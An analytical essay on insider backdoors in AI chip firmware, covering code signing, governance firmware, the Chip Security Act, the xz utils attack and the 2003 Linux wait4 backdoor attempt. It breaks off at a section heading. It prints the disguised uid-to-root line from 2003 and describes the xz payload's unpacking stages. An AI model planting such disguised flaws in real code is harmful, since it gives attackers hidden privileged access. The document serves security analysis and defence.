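# How insiders can plant malicious code in AI chip firmware before it is signed

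## How AI chip firmware is written, signed and checked

Firmware is low-level code that runs on a device's own processors and controls its hardware. In AI chips, such as the graphics processing units (GPUs) that Nvidia sells to data centres, firmware starts the chip, sets voltages and clock speeds, manages memory, and reports the chip's identity and condition to the server that houses it. Manufacturers issue new versions for years after a sale. Because firmware sits below every program that a customer runs, anyone with control of it also controls the chip. Manufacturers therefore attach a cryptographic signature to each version and design their chips to reject firmware without one, which is called code signing.

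A signature lets the chip check who approved a file and that nobody has altered it since, but not whether the file is harmless. An insider, meaning someone who misuses legitimate access to the code, the build system or the signing process, can add a backdoor before the file is signed, and the chip will accept it. A backdoor is hidden logic that gives whoever knows of it access or privileges that others lack. In 2024 a trusted maintainer added one to xz utils, a compression library used on many Linux servers. The problem has become more pressing for AI chips because researchers and legislators want chip software to also enforce or report on rules about who may use the chips and where.

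### From source code to chip

Suppose a developer at a chipmaker wants to fix how a chip reads its temperature sensor. The developer edits the source code, which is the human-readable text of the program, and records the edit as a commit, which shows the changed lines, the author and the date. In code review, a colleague then reads the commit, normally seeing only the changed lines and a little of the code around them. A maintainer, who has authority to accept changes and publish releases, then merges the commit into the main copy of the code. On a small team, the reviewer and the maintainer may well be the same person.

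The chip cannot run source code, so a build system of scripts, compilers and servers turns it into a binary, a file of machine instructions. The build also uses material that nobody looked at when reviewing the temperature fix, such as libraries from other projects, configuration files and the compiler itself. Analysing the finished binary is slow and requires special tools. Reviewers therefore read the source code rather than the binary the chip runs, and they can trust that the two match only as far as they trust the build system.

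The next step is to sign the binary. A program first computes the file's hash, which is a short fingerprint of its contents. SHA-384, a common choice for firmware, produces a 384-bit hash whatever the file's size. Flipping one bit of the file flips about half the bits of the hash, and nobody knows a practical way to find two files with the same hash. The signer then combines the hash *h* with a secret number, the private key, to produce a signature *s*. Anyone with the matching public key can use it to check whether *s* was produced from *h* with the private key, but can't practically use it to work out the private key.

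Anyone who can use the private key can make every chip that relies on it accept any file, so manufacturers usually keep the key in a hardware security module. This tamper-resistant device takes in a hash and returns a signature, and never releases the key. A manufacturer can set the module to sign only when two authorised people both act, a rule called dual control. But the module typically receives just a 384-bit hash, and nobody can tell from a hash what the code does. Before signing, the people at the module can confirm that the hash matches the file the build system delivered and that the release has the required approvals.

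The chip performs the last check, called secure boot, every time it starts. A small program that the manufacturer fixed permanently in the hardware computes the firmware's hash, tests the signature against a public key that the hardware also protects, and stops if the test fails. According to the Nvidia product brief cited in *Near-Term Enforcement of AI Chip Export Controls Using a Firmware-Based Design* (Petrie, 2024), the H100, a data-centre GPU, already has a security controller that authenticates the firmware before the GPU may boot.

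Rollback protection and attestation address two problems that secure boot leaves open. The first is that an old release keeps its valid signature even after someone finds a vulnerability in it. Rollback protection blocks firmware older than a set version, using a counter in the device that can only increase. The second is that someone who isn't near the chip may want to know what it is running. With attestation, the chip collects facts about itself, including its firmware version, and signs the report with a private key unique to that device. The manufacturer keeps a record of each device's public key, so the report can be checked.

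Secure boot and rollback protection protect against people who cannot get their code signed, but not against malicious logic inside an official release. Attestation may even give false reassurance, because a chip running the backdoored release correctly reports that it is running the manufacturer's official firmware. Releasing a fix does not remove the problem on its own. Petrie points out that a chip will run any signed release whose version is above its counter, so a flawed release can remain exploitable indefinitely on chips whose owners never move the counter past it. Petrie is discussing accidental flaws, but a planted flaw would persist in the same way, and a chip owner who benefits from it has good reason not to update.

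### Firmware that enforces rules

Governance firmware makes an AI chip enforce or report on a rule, such as a usage licence or a location check. Petrie's design for "offline licensing" is a useful example because it is deliberately minimal. A chip should stop working unless it holds an up-to-date licence from a regulator, an idea Petrie takes from earlier reports by Aarne and colleagues and by Kulp and colleagues. A stolen or smuggled chip would become useless once its licence ran out.

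Each licence is a small file that names one chip, grants it a number of clock cycles and carries a licence number. The regulator signs it with its own private key, separate from the key the manufacturer uses for firmware. Petrie's example licence grants 10¹⁵ cycles, which would last a little under seven days at 1.7 billion cycles a second, a plausible speed for such a chip.

After secure boot, the firmware looks in the chip's memory for a licence and accepts it if four conditions hold:

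- The device number in the licence equals the chip's own.
- The licence number is greater than the largest one the chip has used so far.
- The allowance is reasonable (it must not be negative, for instance).
- The signature passes the test against the regulator's public key.

The chip then records the licence number, adds the allowance to a usage meter and works normally while the meter counts down. When the meter reaches zero, the chip halts and checks for another licence. If there is none, it sends an error message and does no computing until one arrives.

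Recording used licences is difficult because an attacker who can rewrite the memory that holds the record can keep reusing the same licence. Petrie suggests keeping the record in the same kind of one-way storage as the rollback counter, but a chip may have only tens or hundreds of such bits to spare, so each licence would have to last longer. Alternatively, the chip can put a new random number in a request each time it starts and wait for the regulator to sign that request, so an old reply would not work.

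This mechanism is attractive because it could be deployed quickly. Petrie estimates three months for a proof of concept and six for a more robust version, and thinks that manufacturers could deliver it within a year, ideally to chips already sold, if those chips have a few common security features. Because it needs no new hardware, nearly the whole rule is implemented in firmware. The regulator's public key, for example, is stored in the firmware binary and protected by the manufacturer's signature on that binary. Anyone who gets an additional public key into a signed release can issue licences that the chip will accept, even if the regulator guards its private key flawlessly. The other conditions are just as vulnerable. If the test on licence numbers used "greater than or equal to" instead of "greater than", a one-character difference in most programming languages, a chip could keep reusing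 its latest licence forever.

Location verification checks whether a chip is where the rules allow it to be, and need not disable the chip if it isn't. Transformer's *Chip location verification is the new export control battleground* describes a version in which a "landmark" server at a known place sends a signal to the chip, the chip replies with proof of its identity, and the server times the exchange. Nothing travels faster than light, so a round trip of *t* seconds puts the chip at most *ct*/2 away, where *c* is the speed of light. A reply within 10 milliseconds cannot have come from more than 1,500 kilometres away. For a server in Kuala Lumpur, that rules out Shenzhen, roughly 2,500 kilometres away. Delaying the reply only makes the chip seem further away. To cheat, a smuggler would need a machine near the server that can pass as the missing chip, so the scheme depends on the chip's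 identity key staying secret. Firmware that leaked the key, or signed replies for another machine, could defeat it.

Researchers at the Institute for AI Policy and Strategy, a think tank, estimated that rolling out the firmware update for such checks might cost less than a million dollars, according to Transformer. The landmarks would be 100 to 500 new servers costing about $25,000 each per year, or $2.5 million to $12.5 million a year in total.

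*Flexible Hardware-Enabled Guarantees for AI Compute* (Petrie, Aarne and colleagues, 2025) describes a more ambitious proposal, called flexHEG, that adds hardware. A tamper-proof enclosure holds the AI chip and a "guarantee processor", which sits between the chip and the outside world and can see what passes in and out. The processor's firmware can enforce a set of rules, and the power to set and update them could belong to anyone from the chip's owner to a quorum of states. The enclosure protects against physical attacks such as drilling and probing, but the rules are still firmware that someone has to write, build and approve.

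### Law and practice in December 2026

Offline licensing and flexHEG are research proposals. Location checks are much closer to law, through the Chip Security Act. Senator Tom Cotton introduced the Act in May 2025, and it has a companion bill in the House of Representatives. It would require exported AI chips to have a "chip security mechanism" that helps show whether anyone has diverted them to a forbidden destination. *Amendment to Rules Comm. Print 119–33* (Huizenga, 2026), offered in June 2026, would add a version of the Act to the House's annual defence bill, the National Defense Authorization Act.

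That version lets the Secretary of Commerce choose among different mechanisms, several of which involve no firmware. On-site audits and inventories need only inspectors. A trusted company could also declare periodically that all its chips are accounted for, which would require only some way to check the declaration. (The bill calls these declarations "attestations", but they are unrelated to the signed reports that chips produce.) Timed location checks through a landmark server would use "secure software- or firmware-enabled mechanisms". The text also allows other methods that the Secretary finds convincing.

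Huizenga's text has two limits that affect governance firmware. First, it does not direct the Secretary to require mechanisms that may hinder a chip's functionality, such as a kill switch or geofencing. A licence that halts the chip, as in Petrie's design, seems to be the kind of mechanism the drafters meant. Second, it does not direct the Secretary to require location checks that need physical changes to hardware, which makes software and firmware the more likely place for any check on the chip itself. The Act would therefore probably lead to code that reports on a chip but does not stop it. The text sets no rules for how a manufacturer should review, build or sign that code, although it requires Commerce to study later whether enhanced mechanisms could introduce new vulnerabilities.

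The bill's wording has changed as it has advanced. In the critique *Basic Problems With the Chip Security Act*, Rehman (2026), who disclaims any legal expertise, quotes the text that the House Foreign Affairs Committee passed in March 2026 and notes that the main deadline had grown from 180 days after enactment to one year. Under that text, the final rule "includes" a duty to report failed checks and evidence of tampering, but under the June amendment it "may include" one. This change matters because a pattern of odd failures in the field is one of the few ways outsiders might notice planted code.

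The House passed its defence bill in July by 216 votes to 212 (Williams, 2026, *House narrowly passes $1.15 trillion defense bill*). By November, the Chip Security Act was one of three chip bills under consideration for the Senate's version (Newsroom America, 2026, *Nvidia Privately Told Lawmaker Chip Tracking Is Feasible, Despite Industry Group's Doubts*). On 3 December, Senator Tim Scott, who chairs the Banking Committee, backed a slate of chip bills. The next day, Faisal (2026, *US Congress Moves to Ban Blackwell Chip Sales to China*) reported that Scott had cleared three of them for the defence package, which was the last approval they needed, and that the text could appear within days. The Chip Security Act is probably one of the three, but its inclusion and exact wording won't be certain until negotiators release the final text.

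The chip industry has publicly questioned whether the checks would work. In March 2026, the Semiconductor Industry Association, to which Nvidia belongs, called the tracking mandates "new, untested, and potentially infeasible." According to Newsroom America, Representative Bill Foster, a cosponsor of the Act, has since said that Nvidia's representatives told him in technical discussions, though never in writing, that of course the company could do it.

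Nvidia announced its own requirement for location checks on 30 November 2026. "Neocloud" providers outside the United States, newer companies that mostly rent out AI computing, must use its Fleet Intelligence tool, which lets customers verify the identity and location of their chips for US government audits. The tool already covers more than 100,000 data-centre GPUs. EconoTimes' *Nvidia Requires Emerging Overseas Cloud Providers to Track GPU Locations* (2026) describes it as software that providers deploy to check whether chips are where they should be, using server telemetry and communication delays. Nvidia did not specify in its announcement whether the tool needs particular firmware. The tool may well depend on firmware indirectly, since a delay measurement is weak evidence of a chip's location unless the chip can also prove its identity. Nvidia's other safeguard, checks at customer sites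 after shipment, does not depend on firmware.

### Who could change what

Petrie argues that the most worrying attacks are those that scale to thousands of chips at low cost. Tampering with the wires that feed a usage meter takes delicate work on every chip, whereas planting code takes the same work whether it reaches one chip or a million, and the manufacturer distributes the code for free.

Petrie briefly mentions this attack. An adversary could make modified firmware look legitimate by stealing the manufacturer's private key, or by getting an employee to introduce a backdoor or create a modified version. To protect the regulator's key, Petrie suggests requiring several regulators to sign each licence, perhaps two thirds of an approved group. For the manufacturer's key, the advice is to keep it secure, which helps against theft but not against a backdoor already inside an apparently normal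 release when it is signed. Petrie also recommends testing each firmware version thoroughly and having auditors and researchers with no ties to chipmakers review the design. The stated reason for the review is that chipmakers may put low cost and customer convenience first. The review could also catch a backdoor planted by an insider, but only if the reviewers examine the code that ships.

"An employee" covers several jobs, and they give access to different things:

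- A developer can propose changes to the source code, and often to the tests and build scripts stored beside it. The malicious lines have to get past a reviewer, so they need to look innocent or like an honest mistake.
- A maintainer can accept changes, decide who reviews them and choose what goes into a release. Where the project's rules allow it, a maintainer can also merge code that nobody else has read.
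- A build engineer can alter the compiler, the scripts, the libraries or the server. The binary then contains something that the source code does not, and a reviewer who reads every line of the source will find nothing wrong.
- A signer cannot edit an approved binary without changing its hash. But a signer can submit the hash of some other file, such as a private version of the firmware meant for a few customers. Dual control addresses this last possibility most directly, because a second person has to approve the request.

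A malicious developer, maintainer or build engineer does not need access to the signing key. If nobody catches their changes before signing, honest signers will sign the firmware without knowing it contains malicious code.

An insider might have either of two goals, which call for different code. The first is to switch off a rule for some chips. A smuggling network, or a government that wants more computing power than its licences allow, would want its own chips to skip the usage meter or report false locations while the rule still applies to all other chips. The hidden code could check for certain device numbers or for a licence with an unusual feature. The owners of the affected chips are complicit and will not complain, and the regulator receives reports that look normal. Physical inspection might still expose the fraud by finding chips that are missing from their approved site or running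 without a valid licence.

The other aim is hidden control over all of the chips, meaning the ability to halt them, corrupt their results or copy the data they process. Almost every owner is then a victim with a motive to search for the backdoor and report anything strange, and a security researcher can buy an affected chip and take it apart. The xz utils backdoor was similar in that it shipped to everyone and could be used by whoever held the right key. Governance firmware could make the insider's job easier. A chip built to Petrie's design already contains a routine for shutting itself down, so an insider would only need to add a secret way to set the meter to zero. Foreign customers have already considered this risk. When Chinese authorities questioned the security of Nvidia's chips in 2025, the company replied that they contain no kill switches or backdoors, according to Transformer.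 A customer who doubts that answer cannot verify it by checking the signature, because code planted before signing is signed along with the rest of the firmware.

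## The xz utils backdoor: a trusted maintainer's malicious release

In February 2024, a maintainer of xz utils using the name "Jia Tan" published a release containing a backdoor and signed it with a genuine key. The backdoor would have let anyone with a certain private key run commands on affected Linux servers without logging in. Jia Tan had earned the credentials over more than two years and did not need to steal them. Most of the project's work was public, so researchers could reconstruct the attack in far more detail than companies usually publish about their own insiders.

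### How Jia Tan became a maintainer

Linux distributions, such as Debian and Fedora, combine thousands of programs into a working operating system, and their package installers depend on xz utils. Lasse Collin had maintained it since 2009 as an unpaid hobby. Przymus and Durieux (2025), in *Wolves in the Repository*, suggest that the project appealed to an attacker partly because it had a single developer, little traffic and around ten active people in its chat channel.

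Jia Tan's first contribution, on 29 October 2021, was a settings file for text editors. A fix for an apparent problem with reproducible builds followed a month later. In *Timeline of the xz open source attack*, Cox (2024) finds nothing wrong with these patches, even in retrospect. Jia Tan also reviewed other people's code, reasonably well according to Przymus and Durieux. In November 2021 the same account made an odd-looking change to a different project, replacing a text-printing function in the libarchive library with a less secure one, and the maintainers there accepted it. In *On the critical path to implant backdoors*, Lins, Mayrhofer and colleagues (2024) could not tell whether this change was related to the later attack.

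Collin began merging Jia Tan's work in February 2022. From April, other accounts complained on the project's mailing list that he was too slow. "Jigar Kumar" complained about an unmerged patch of Jia Tan's, although Collin had already accepted four others, and "Dennis Ens" asked whether anyone still maintained the Java version. In June, Kumar wrote that there would be no progress without a new maintainer. Collin answered that long-term mental health issues had limited his ability to care for the project, and that it was an unpaid hobby. Ens expressed sympathy and suggested that he hand over part of the project. By the end of the month, Collin was describing Jia Tan as "practically a co-maintainer already".

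Many of these email addresses appear nowhere else online, even in leaked data, so Cox thinks somebody probably invented the accounts to push Collin into sharing control. Przymus and Durieux counted eight new people on the mailing list during this phase, where only 29 had been active before. Six of the eight never took part at any other time, though some of them may have been ordinary users who lost interest.

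Collin gave up control in small steps. In November 2022 he added Jia Tan to the address for bug reports, and on 30 December Jia Tan merged changes directly into the main copy of the code for the first time. As a co-maintainer, Jia Tan could now add code without anyone's approval, as The Intercept (2024) reported. By Cox's account Jia Tan published their first release, version 5.4.2, in March 2023. (Przymus and Durieux put the first release three months earlier.)

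The project also moved to GitHub, a website that hosts code. Przymus and Durieux write that Jia Tan created the project's organisation account there in December 2022 and so owned it, but Cox writes that Jia Tan joined an existing organisation in October. Either way, Jia Tan used the move to gain influence, replacing Collin's email address with their own in the template for reporting problems and, in January 2024, moving the project's website to GitHub as well. Collin kept sole control of the older tukaani.org server, as he explains in Tukaani's *xz backdoor*, his public statement on the incident.

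To see what Jia Tan had contributed, Przymus and Durieux collected 1,020 commits, 307 mailing-list messages and other records, and classified the lines each commit changed. They say the account was active for 2.6 years, although their start and end dates are about 2.4 years apart. Only eight commits were malicious, all from 2024. Most of the rest was documentation and translation, and the number of languages suggests that Jia Tan used automatic translation or copied from other projects. Such work is easy to produce in quantity and attracts little scrutiny. Jia Tan was also more active than Collin in announcing releases and answering users' questions.

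After the attack, Collin reviewed the commits. In Tukaani's review notes, he marks most of them as OK, sometimes after making small corrections. He had fixed a memory leak in one, and another contained a copy-and-paste error, the kind of mistake any regular contributor makes.

Jia Tan may have been more than one person. In *Towards Socio-Technical Topology-Aware Adaptive Threat Detection in Software Supply Chains*, Welsh, Finnsson and colleagues (2025) used an algorithm to group the account's GitHub posts by sentence length, punctuation, sentiment and other features. The posts fitted best into two groups, one common in early 2023 and again around the time of the backdoor, and the other dominant from mid-2023. This is weak evidence, because one person's style also changes with mood and subject. The researchers also found that Jia Tan changed about 132 lines on average each time they altered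 a file, compared with 47 for Collin, and that the largest changes came around the insertion of the backdoor. An alarm based on such figures might have drawn attention to Jia Tan, but it would also go off for an honest newcomer who adds a lot of documentation.

### How the backdoor worked

The backdoor targeted OpenSSH, the program administrators use to log in remotely to most Linux servers. Debian, Fedora and some other distributions modify OpenSSH to notify systemd, the program that manages a server's background services, when it has started. The modified version loads a systemd library, which in turn loaded liblzma, the compression library in xz utils. Malicious code in liblzma could therefore run inside the SSH server, with the server's privileges, even though OpenSSH does not itself use xz utils.

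The first of two changes in mid-2023 that prepared for the backdoor came in June, when an account named "Hans Jansen" contributed code that used ifunc (GNU indirect function). Ifunc lets a library contain several versions of a function, and a small routine called a resolver selects the fastest one for the processor when a program starts. Resolvers run before the system locks the table that lists where each function is in memory, so a malicious resolver can alter that table. Collin reworked the patches, which offered a small gain in speed, and Jia Tan merged the final version. Cox acknowledges that this could have been an innocent optimisation, but Hans Jansen has no other presence on the internet and returned in 2024 to urge Debian to adopt the backdoored release.

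In July 2023 Jia Tan had ifunc switched off in the version of xz utils that Google tests through OSS-Fuzz, a free service that feeds open-source programs large amounts of malformed input to expose bugs, a technique called fuzzing. Jia Tan said that ifunc did not work with one of the memory checkers, and Lins and colleagues agree that there were compatibility problems. OSS-Fuzz lets a project's maintainers decide what it tests, and Collin had confirmed to OSS-Fuzz in March that Jia Tan was a co-maintainer. An automatic check found that Jia Tan had contributed to xz utils and was one of its listed contacts, so it labelled the request ready to merge, and approval followed quickly. Fuzzing might have missed the backdoor anyway, because the malicious code entered the library only when somebody built it as a package for Debian, Fedora or a similar distribution.

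The malicious program, or payload, entered the public repository on 23 February 2024 inside two compressed test files. Developers test compression libraries on unusual and damaged files. According to a note in the folder that predated Jia Tan's involvement, people had made many of the files by hand and no better "source code" for them existed. A reviewer who opened either malicious file would have seen what looked like meaningless bytes, as expected.

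These files did nothing until a build script named build-to-host.m4 unpacked them. Jia Tan put the malicious version of that script only in the release archive, the bundle of source code that distributions download, and not in the repository. Jia Tan published the archive as version 5.6.0 the next day. Release archives for this kind of software normally contain generated build files that the repository lacks (one in the later, clean version 5.8.1 is more than 26,000 lines long), so an extra script did not look out of place.

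Cox's *The xz attack shell script* (2024) takes the build stage apart line by line. In outline:

1. The altered script searches the source folder for a file with a particular marker in it. Only one of the two test files matches.
2. The script swaps certain bytes in that file, which makes an apparently corrupt file valid again, then decompresses it and runs the result as a second script.
3. The second script decompresses the other test file, repeatedly discards 1,024 bytes and keeps the next 2,048, and undoes a simple substitution cipher on the final part of what remains. Decompressing that part gives a third script.
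4. The third script stops unless the build is for 64-bit Linux on Intel-compatible processors, with the expected compiler, and for a Debian or RPM package (Fedora uses the latter format). Otherwise it changes the build instructions so that the finished library includes the malicious code.

Andres Freund, the engineer who discovered the backdoor, suspected that it was restricted to package builds to hinder investigators. His report, *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024), describes how the finished code first runs through an ifunc resolver when the SSH server starts. The code checks that it is inside the SSH server and looks for signs of debugging tools. It then waits until the system looks up RSA_public_decrypt, a function for checking signatures at login, and redirects that entry to its own code. Logins with an RSA key then pass through the backdoor.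 According to Lins and colleagues, the malicious function runs a command taken from the visitor's certificate, but only if the visitor has the attacker's private key. Other logins go on to the normal check.

Version 5.6.0 caused errors in Valgrind, a tool that finds memory mistakes in programs. On 8 March Jia Tan committed a misleading fix, and the next day replaced the two test files with corrected ones. In the commit message, Jia Tan wrote that the originals had been made with random data, and that the new files used a fixed seed so that others could reproduce them. Version 5.6.1 followed the same day. Its build script could also load further instructions from any new test file with the right markers, so Jia Tan could add code later without having to justify changing the existing files.

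In a separate and plainly visible piece of sabotage, a commit in late February added a stray full stop to a build file, at the start of a line in a small test program. The program checked whether a computer supported Landlock, a Linux feature that restricts what a program may do. The full stop prevented the test from compiling, so the build always treated Landlock as unavailable. Cox could not establish the purpose of the change, since it affected the xz command rather than the library that OpenSSH loads. The commit lists Collin as the committer, and Cox thinks he probably overlooked the typo. According to Tukaani's review notes, Collin found no sign that anyone had forged committers' names, which fits that explanation.

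### Whose signatures the release carried

Jia Tan created and signed both backdoored archives, according to Tukaani's statement. The signing key was Jia Tan's own. A post on Openwall's security mailing list (2024) describes it as a 4,096-bit RSA key created on 28 December 2022 and set to expire five years later. Two days after creating the key, Jia Tan merged changes directly for the first time.

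Distributions had accepted this key long before the attack. Persson pointed out on a Fedora mailing list that Fedora's xz package included the public key from 4 May 2023. James (2023) added it to Gentoo, another distribution, the next day in *sec-keys/openpgp-keys-jiatan*. A more careful check of the key's origins would have supported adding it, because Collin had signed it. Users of OpenPGP, the signing system involved, vouch for each other's keys in this way. When a colleague later asked what chain of trust had justified adding the key, James (2024) replied that Jia Tan had become release manager with Collin's consent and that no such verification would have helped.

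Persson thought that either Jia Tan had prepared the attack over a long time or somebody had stolen an honest developer's key and passwords. The signature would be valid in either case, so nobody could tell from it which had happened. Freund thought theft less likely because the account had spent weeks discussing the supposed fixes on several mailing lists.

The case also shows that requiring signatures can lead people to choose a malicious file. GitHub automatically generates an archive of each release from the repository, and that archive lacked the script that unpacked the payload. But Lins and colleagues explain that the developer does not sign these automatic archives, whereas Jia Tan did sign the ones uploaded by hand. A distribution that required a maintainer's signature would therefore have chosen the backdoored archive.

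The distributions then added their own signatures. Optimized by Otto's *Could the XZ backdoor have been detected*, a Debian developer's audit, shows the procedure for version 5.8.1. A Debian packager signs a control file that lists the hashes of the project's archive, the project's signature and Debian's packaging instructions. Anyone can then confirm that Debian is using the archive the project published, but not that the packager read it. Debian's servers compile the package, and Debian signs an index of hashes that lets users' computers check the binary before installing it.

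A Debian user who installed version 5.6.0 relied on signatures from Jia Tan, a packager and Debian. The packager and Debian did not know that the release contained a backdoor. Their signatures showed only that the file had arrived intact from the previous stage, so they added no assurance about its contents to Jia Tan's.

### How Freund found it and how far it had spread

Freund, who works on the PostgreSQL database at Microsoft and stressed that he was not a security researcher, found the backdoor by accident. On computers running Debian's unstable version, he noticed that SSH logins were using a lot of processor time and that Valgrind was reporting errors. In his test, a failed login took 0.3 seconds without the backdoored library and 0.8 seconds with it. The malicious code caused the delay by searching tables in memory for the functions it was designed to replace. Freund recorded what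 the processor did with the backdoor active and inactive, then compared the recordings to find where they diverged. He first suspected Debian's package but then found that the problem came from xz utils itself. He warned Debian and other distributions privately on 28 March 2024, 33 days after the release of version 5.6.0, and published his findings the next day.

The attacker may have rushed the release. On 29 February a developer proposed that the systemd library stop loading liblzma, as part of a general effort to reduce dependencies, and systemd's maintainers accepted the change on 5 March. Once distributions adopted it, the backdoor could no longer have reached the SSH server. Cox cites speculation that the attacker knew about the change and moved faster because of it, which could help explain the faults in version 5.6.0.

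By the time Freund gave his warning, the release was in Debian's unstable and testing versions, Fedora's development version and the Fedora 40 beta. openSUSE had also distributed it. These were mostly versions for developers and testers, not the stable ones that most servers run. Jia Tan asked Ubuntu to adopt version 5.6.1 on the day of the private warning. Neither Przymus and Durieux nor Lins and colleagues know of anyone using the backdoor.

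Debian withdrew the release the same day by shipping the older version 5.4.5 under the number "5.6.1+really5.4.5-1", because its package manager installs an update automatically only if the number is higher. A chipmaker could face the same difficulty if rollback protection had already blocked the last clean firmware. It would then have to give the old code a higher version number and sign it again.

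During the cleanup, Debian suspended its builds and rebuilt its build machines in case the malicious library had affected them. Collin had to check almost three years of commits for other malicious changes, and he removed the ifunc code altogether. He published a clean version on 29 May 2024, two months after the discovery.

Some copies remained available much longer. Binarly, a firmware security company, searched Docker Hub, a public library of container images, which are ready-made bundles of an operating system and other software. Its *Persistent Risk* (2025) reported in August that 12 Debian images still contained the backdoor. Including images that other people had built on top of these, the total was more than 35. The real number could well be larger, because Docker Hub has nearly 12 million repositories and Binarly checked only a small selection, all based on Debian. The practical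 danger is limited, since an attacker would need the right private key and network access to a container running an SSH server. Debian's maintainers declined to remove the images, calling them "historical artifacts", according to TechRadar's *Docker could still be hosting a whole load of potentially malicious images*.

### Which defences would have stopped it

Lins and colleagues made a preliminary assessment of standard defences within weeks of the discovery. They divided the attack into five stages, from building trust to using the backdoor, and asked what might have interrupted each one.

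Defences against stolen accounts, such as a second login factor or signatures on individual commits, would have done little because Jia Tan was using their own account. A transparency log helps an honest developer notice a release that somebody else made with their key, but Jia Tan could have logged the malicious release as normal. Proof of identity for new maintainers would have been a bigger obstacle, and Debian already has its package maintainers meet in person and check identity documents before they sign each other's keys. But Lins and colleagues acknowledge that attackers can steal an identity, or bribe or blackmail someone with a real one.

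They also suggest that a second person should approve every change before it enters the main copy of the code. Jia Tan added the test files directly, without review, but a reviewer probably would not have objected. Optimized by Otto concludes that a diligent Debian packager could not reasonably have spotted the backdoor, and that only another xz developer might have wondered why Jia Tan added test data without test code. However, Collin explains in Tukaani's review notes that the project's test script automatically picks up whatever files are in the folder, so a commit containing only data was not unusual. Reviewers of commits also could not have seen the altered build script, because it was never committed. A packager who compared the script with the standard version might have noticed that its version number was 30, when genuine copies elsewhere in Debian had numbers such as 3 or 5, but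 that would have meant checking every such file in every package.

Building from the repository would have defeated this attack. Without the altered script, the test files were harmless, as Tukaani's statement confirms. A reproducible build would not have been enough, since anyone who started from the malicious archive would have reproduced the backdoor. Lins and colleagues recommend that distributions take their source from the repository, or that projects create release archives through an automated process that others can inspect. They examined about 61 Debian packages on which popular internet-facing servers depend. Only 10 used the archive that the hosting site generates from the repository, and for nine they could not identify where the code came from. If all distributions had built from the repository, Jia Tan would have had to put the trigger there too, where more people could have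 seen it. The attack would have been harder but still possible, as the unnoticed full stop in the Landlock test suggests.

They also recommend storing the commands that generate test files, which a reviewer can read, instead of the ready-made files. This would have removed the backdoor's hiding place. Collin seems to have reached a similar view. His notes say he left one test in place in case somebody adds proper files "along with a generator program".

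Sandboxing could have contained the damage. Lins and colleagues propose running compression code and similar libraries in separate processes with few privileges, as web browsers do with many of their components. The xz backdoor altered the SSH server's memory, so it would have failed if the library had run in a separate process. Sandboxing slows programs and, more importantly, creates extra work for developers, because they must adapt most sandboxing tools to each case.

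Two of the suggestions from Lins and colleagues concern motives. Better-funded maintainers would have more time for review and would be more expensive to bribe. Prosecution might deter some attackers, but intelligence services are rarely prosecuted, and Lins and colleagues speculate from the attack's length and complexity that a sophisticated organisation with stable funding was behind it. They expect that other ways in would remain even if projects adopted all of these measures.

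### Would the same attack work at a chipmaker?

A chipmaker has several advantages over Collin. It pays its staff, knows who they are and can take them to court, while nobody has publicly established who Jia Tan was. Strangers on a mailing list cannot pressure it into appointing a new release manager. It can also require a second reviewer for every change and build each release on a central server directly from the repository, which would close the gap that Jia Tan exploited. These measures work only if the company enforces them, including for the senior engineers who administer the repository and the build server.

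Employment is a weaker safeguard than it may seem. Lins and colleagues call the deterrent effect of contracts "rather weak", because a careful attacker will leave room for an innocent explanation. Instead of spending two years building a false identity, an attacker could also bribe or threaten an engineer who already has access, which vetting at hiring cannot rule out.

An insider on a firmware team could gain trust much as Jia Tan did. Someone who willingly maintains the build scripts, updates test data and prepares releases will collect permissions that colleagues are happy to give up. Firmware projects can also contain binary files that few people can read, such as calibration data or code from suppliers. A chipmaker that uses open-source libraries also depends on maintainers like Collin and Jia Tan, whom it has never vetted.

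The biggest difference is who can investigate. Freund had the source code, could compare the release archive with the repository, and could run the old and new libraries on his own computer while recording what the processor did. A customer with a suspicious AI chip usually has only the signed binary, and secure boot prevents them from running a modified copy to see what changes. Optimized by Otto argues that hiding a backdoor in closed-source software is "relatively trivial" and that customers have to trust the vendor. This view, from a committed open-source developer, overlooks the vendor's own reviewers, who can read all the code, although there are fewer of them and they all work for the same employer. Lins and colleagues report that many experts who studied the xz case believe similar attacks are possible on proprietary code.

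The first clue, however, was a half-second delay rather than anything in the code, although the malicious release had been public for almost five weeks. Chip customers can also measure delays, and large ones monitor their hardware closely, but a hidden exemption for certain device numbers in governance firmware would add only a tiny fraction of a second. Much of the xz delay arose because the attacker had to get from a compression library into a different program and find the right function there, whereas an insider who writes governance firmware already works on the code that enforces the rule.

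The xz release also had to pass through test versions of Linux, run by people who like to investigate odd behaviour, before it could reach most servers. A chipmaker can send new firmware to a few customers first, but they would mainly find faults that affect their own chips and would be unlikely to discover an exemption for someone else's chips.

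## Malicious source code that looks like an honest mistake

Jia Tan hid the xz backdoor in files that reviewers rarely read. An insider on a firmware team could instead put a flaw in ordinary source code and rely on colleagues to mistake it for correct code. The change can be as small as one character. If a reviewer spots it, the insider can claim it was a mistake, fix it and keep their job.

### One wrong character

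In 2003 the developers of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, kept the master copy of its source code in a system called BitKeeper. Some of them refused to use BitKeeper, so the project also maintained a duplicate in another system, CVS. On 5 November Larry McVoy, whose company made BitKeeper, noticed a change in the duplicate that had no link to a record of approval and did not exist in the master copy. According to Princeton CITP's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003*, somebody had apparently broken into the CVS server and added two lines to wait4, a function that lets one program wait for another to finish. The first line was:

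`if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))`

The second line set an error code, so the pair looked like a routine check that rejects an unusual combination of options. In C, the language of the kernel, `==` compares two values, while `=` changes the value on its left. The first half of the first line is a comparison, true only for a program that requests that odd combination. The second half uses `=` to set the program's user ID to 0, which belongs to "root", a user who may do anything on the system. An assignment in C also has a value, here 0, which C treats as false. The condition therefore fails, the second line never runs, and the program carries on with root's privileges.

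Compilers often warn about a single equals sign in a condition, but Szepe (2003) pointed out on the kernel mailing list that the extra parentheses around the assignment prevent that warning. Even McVoy did not see the problem in the line at first, and replied "Good eyes, I missed that" when another developer explained it (McVoy, 2003).

The intruder had attributed the change to David Miller, a long-standing kernel developer, according to Slashdot's *Linux Kernel Back-Door Hack Attempt Discovered*. Debian's vulnerability database entry, *CVE-2003-1161*, states that no release ever contained it. In InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013), the kernel developer Jonathan Corbet explains that every change in CVS carried a link to its BitKeeper counterpart, so one without a link stood out immediately. The missing link led people to read the code, so the case only partly fits the claim by Kokkonis, Marcozzi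 and Zacchiroli in *Not In My Git Yard* (2026) that only luck and manual review have stopped known attempts to plant backdoors in widely used projects. An insider's commit would have had a genuine link, so this check would not have flagged it.

### A swapped constant

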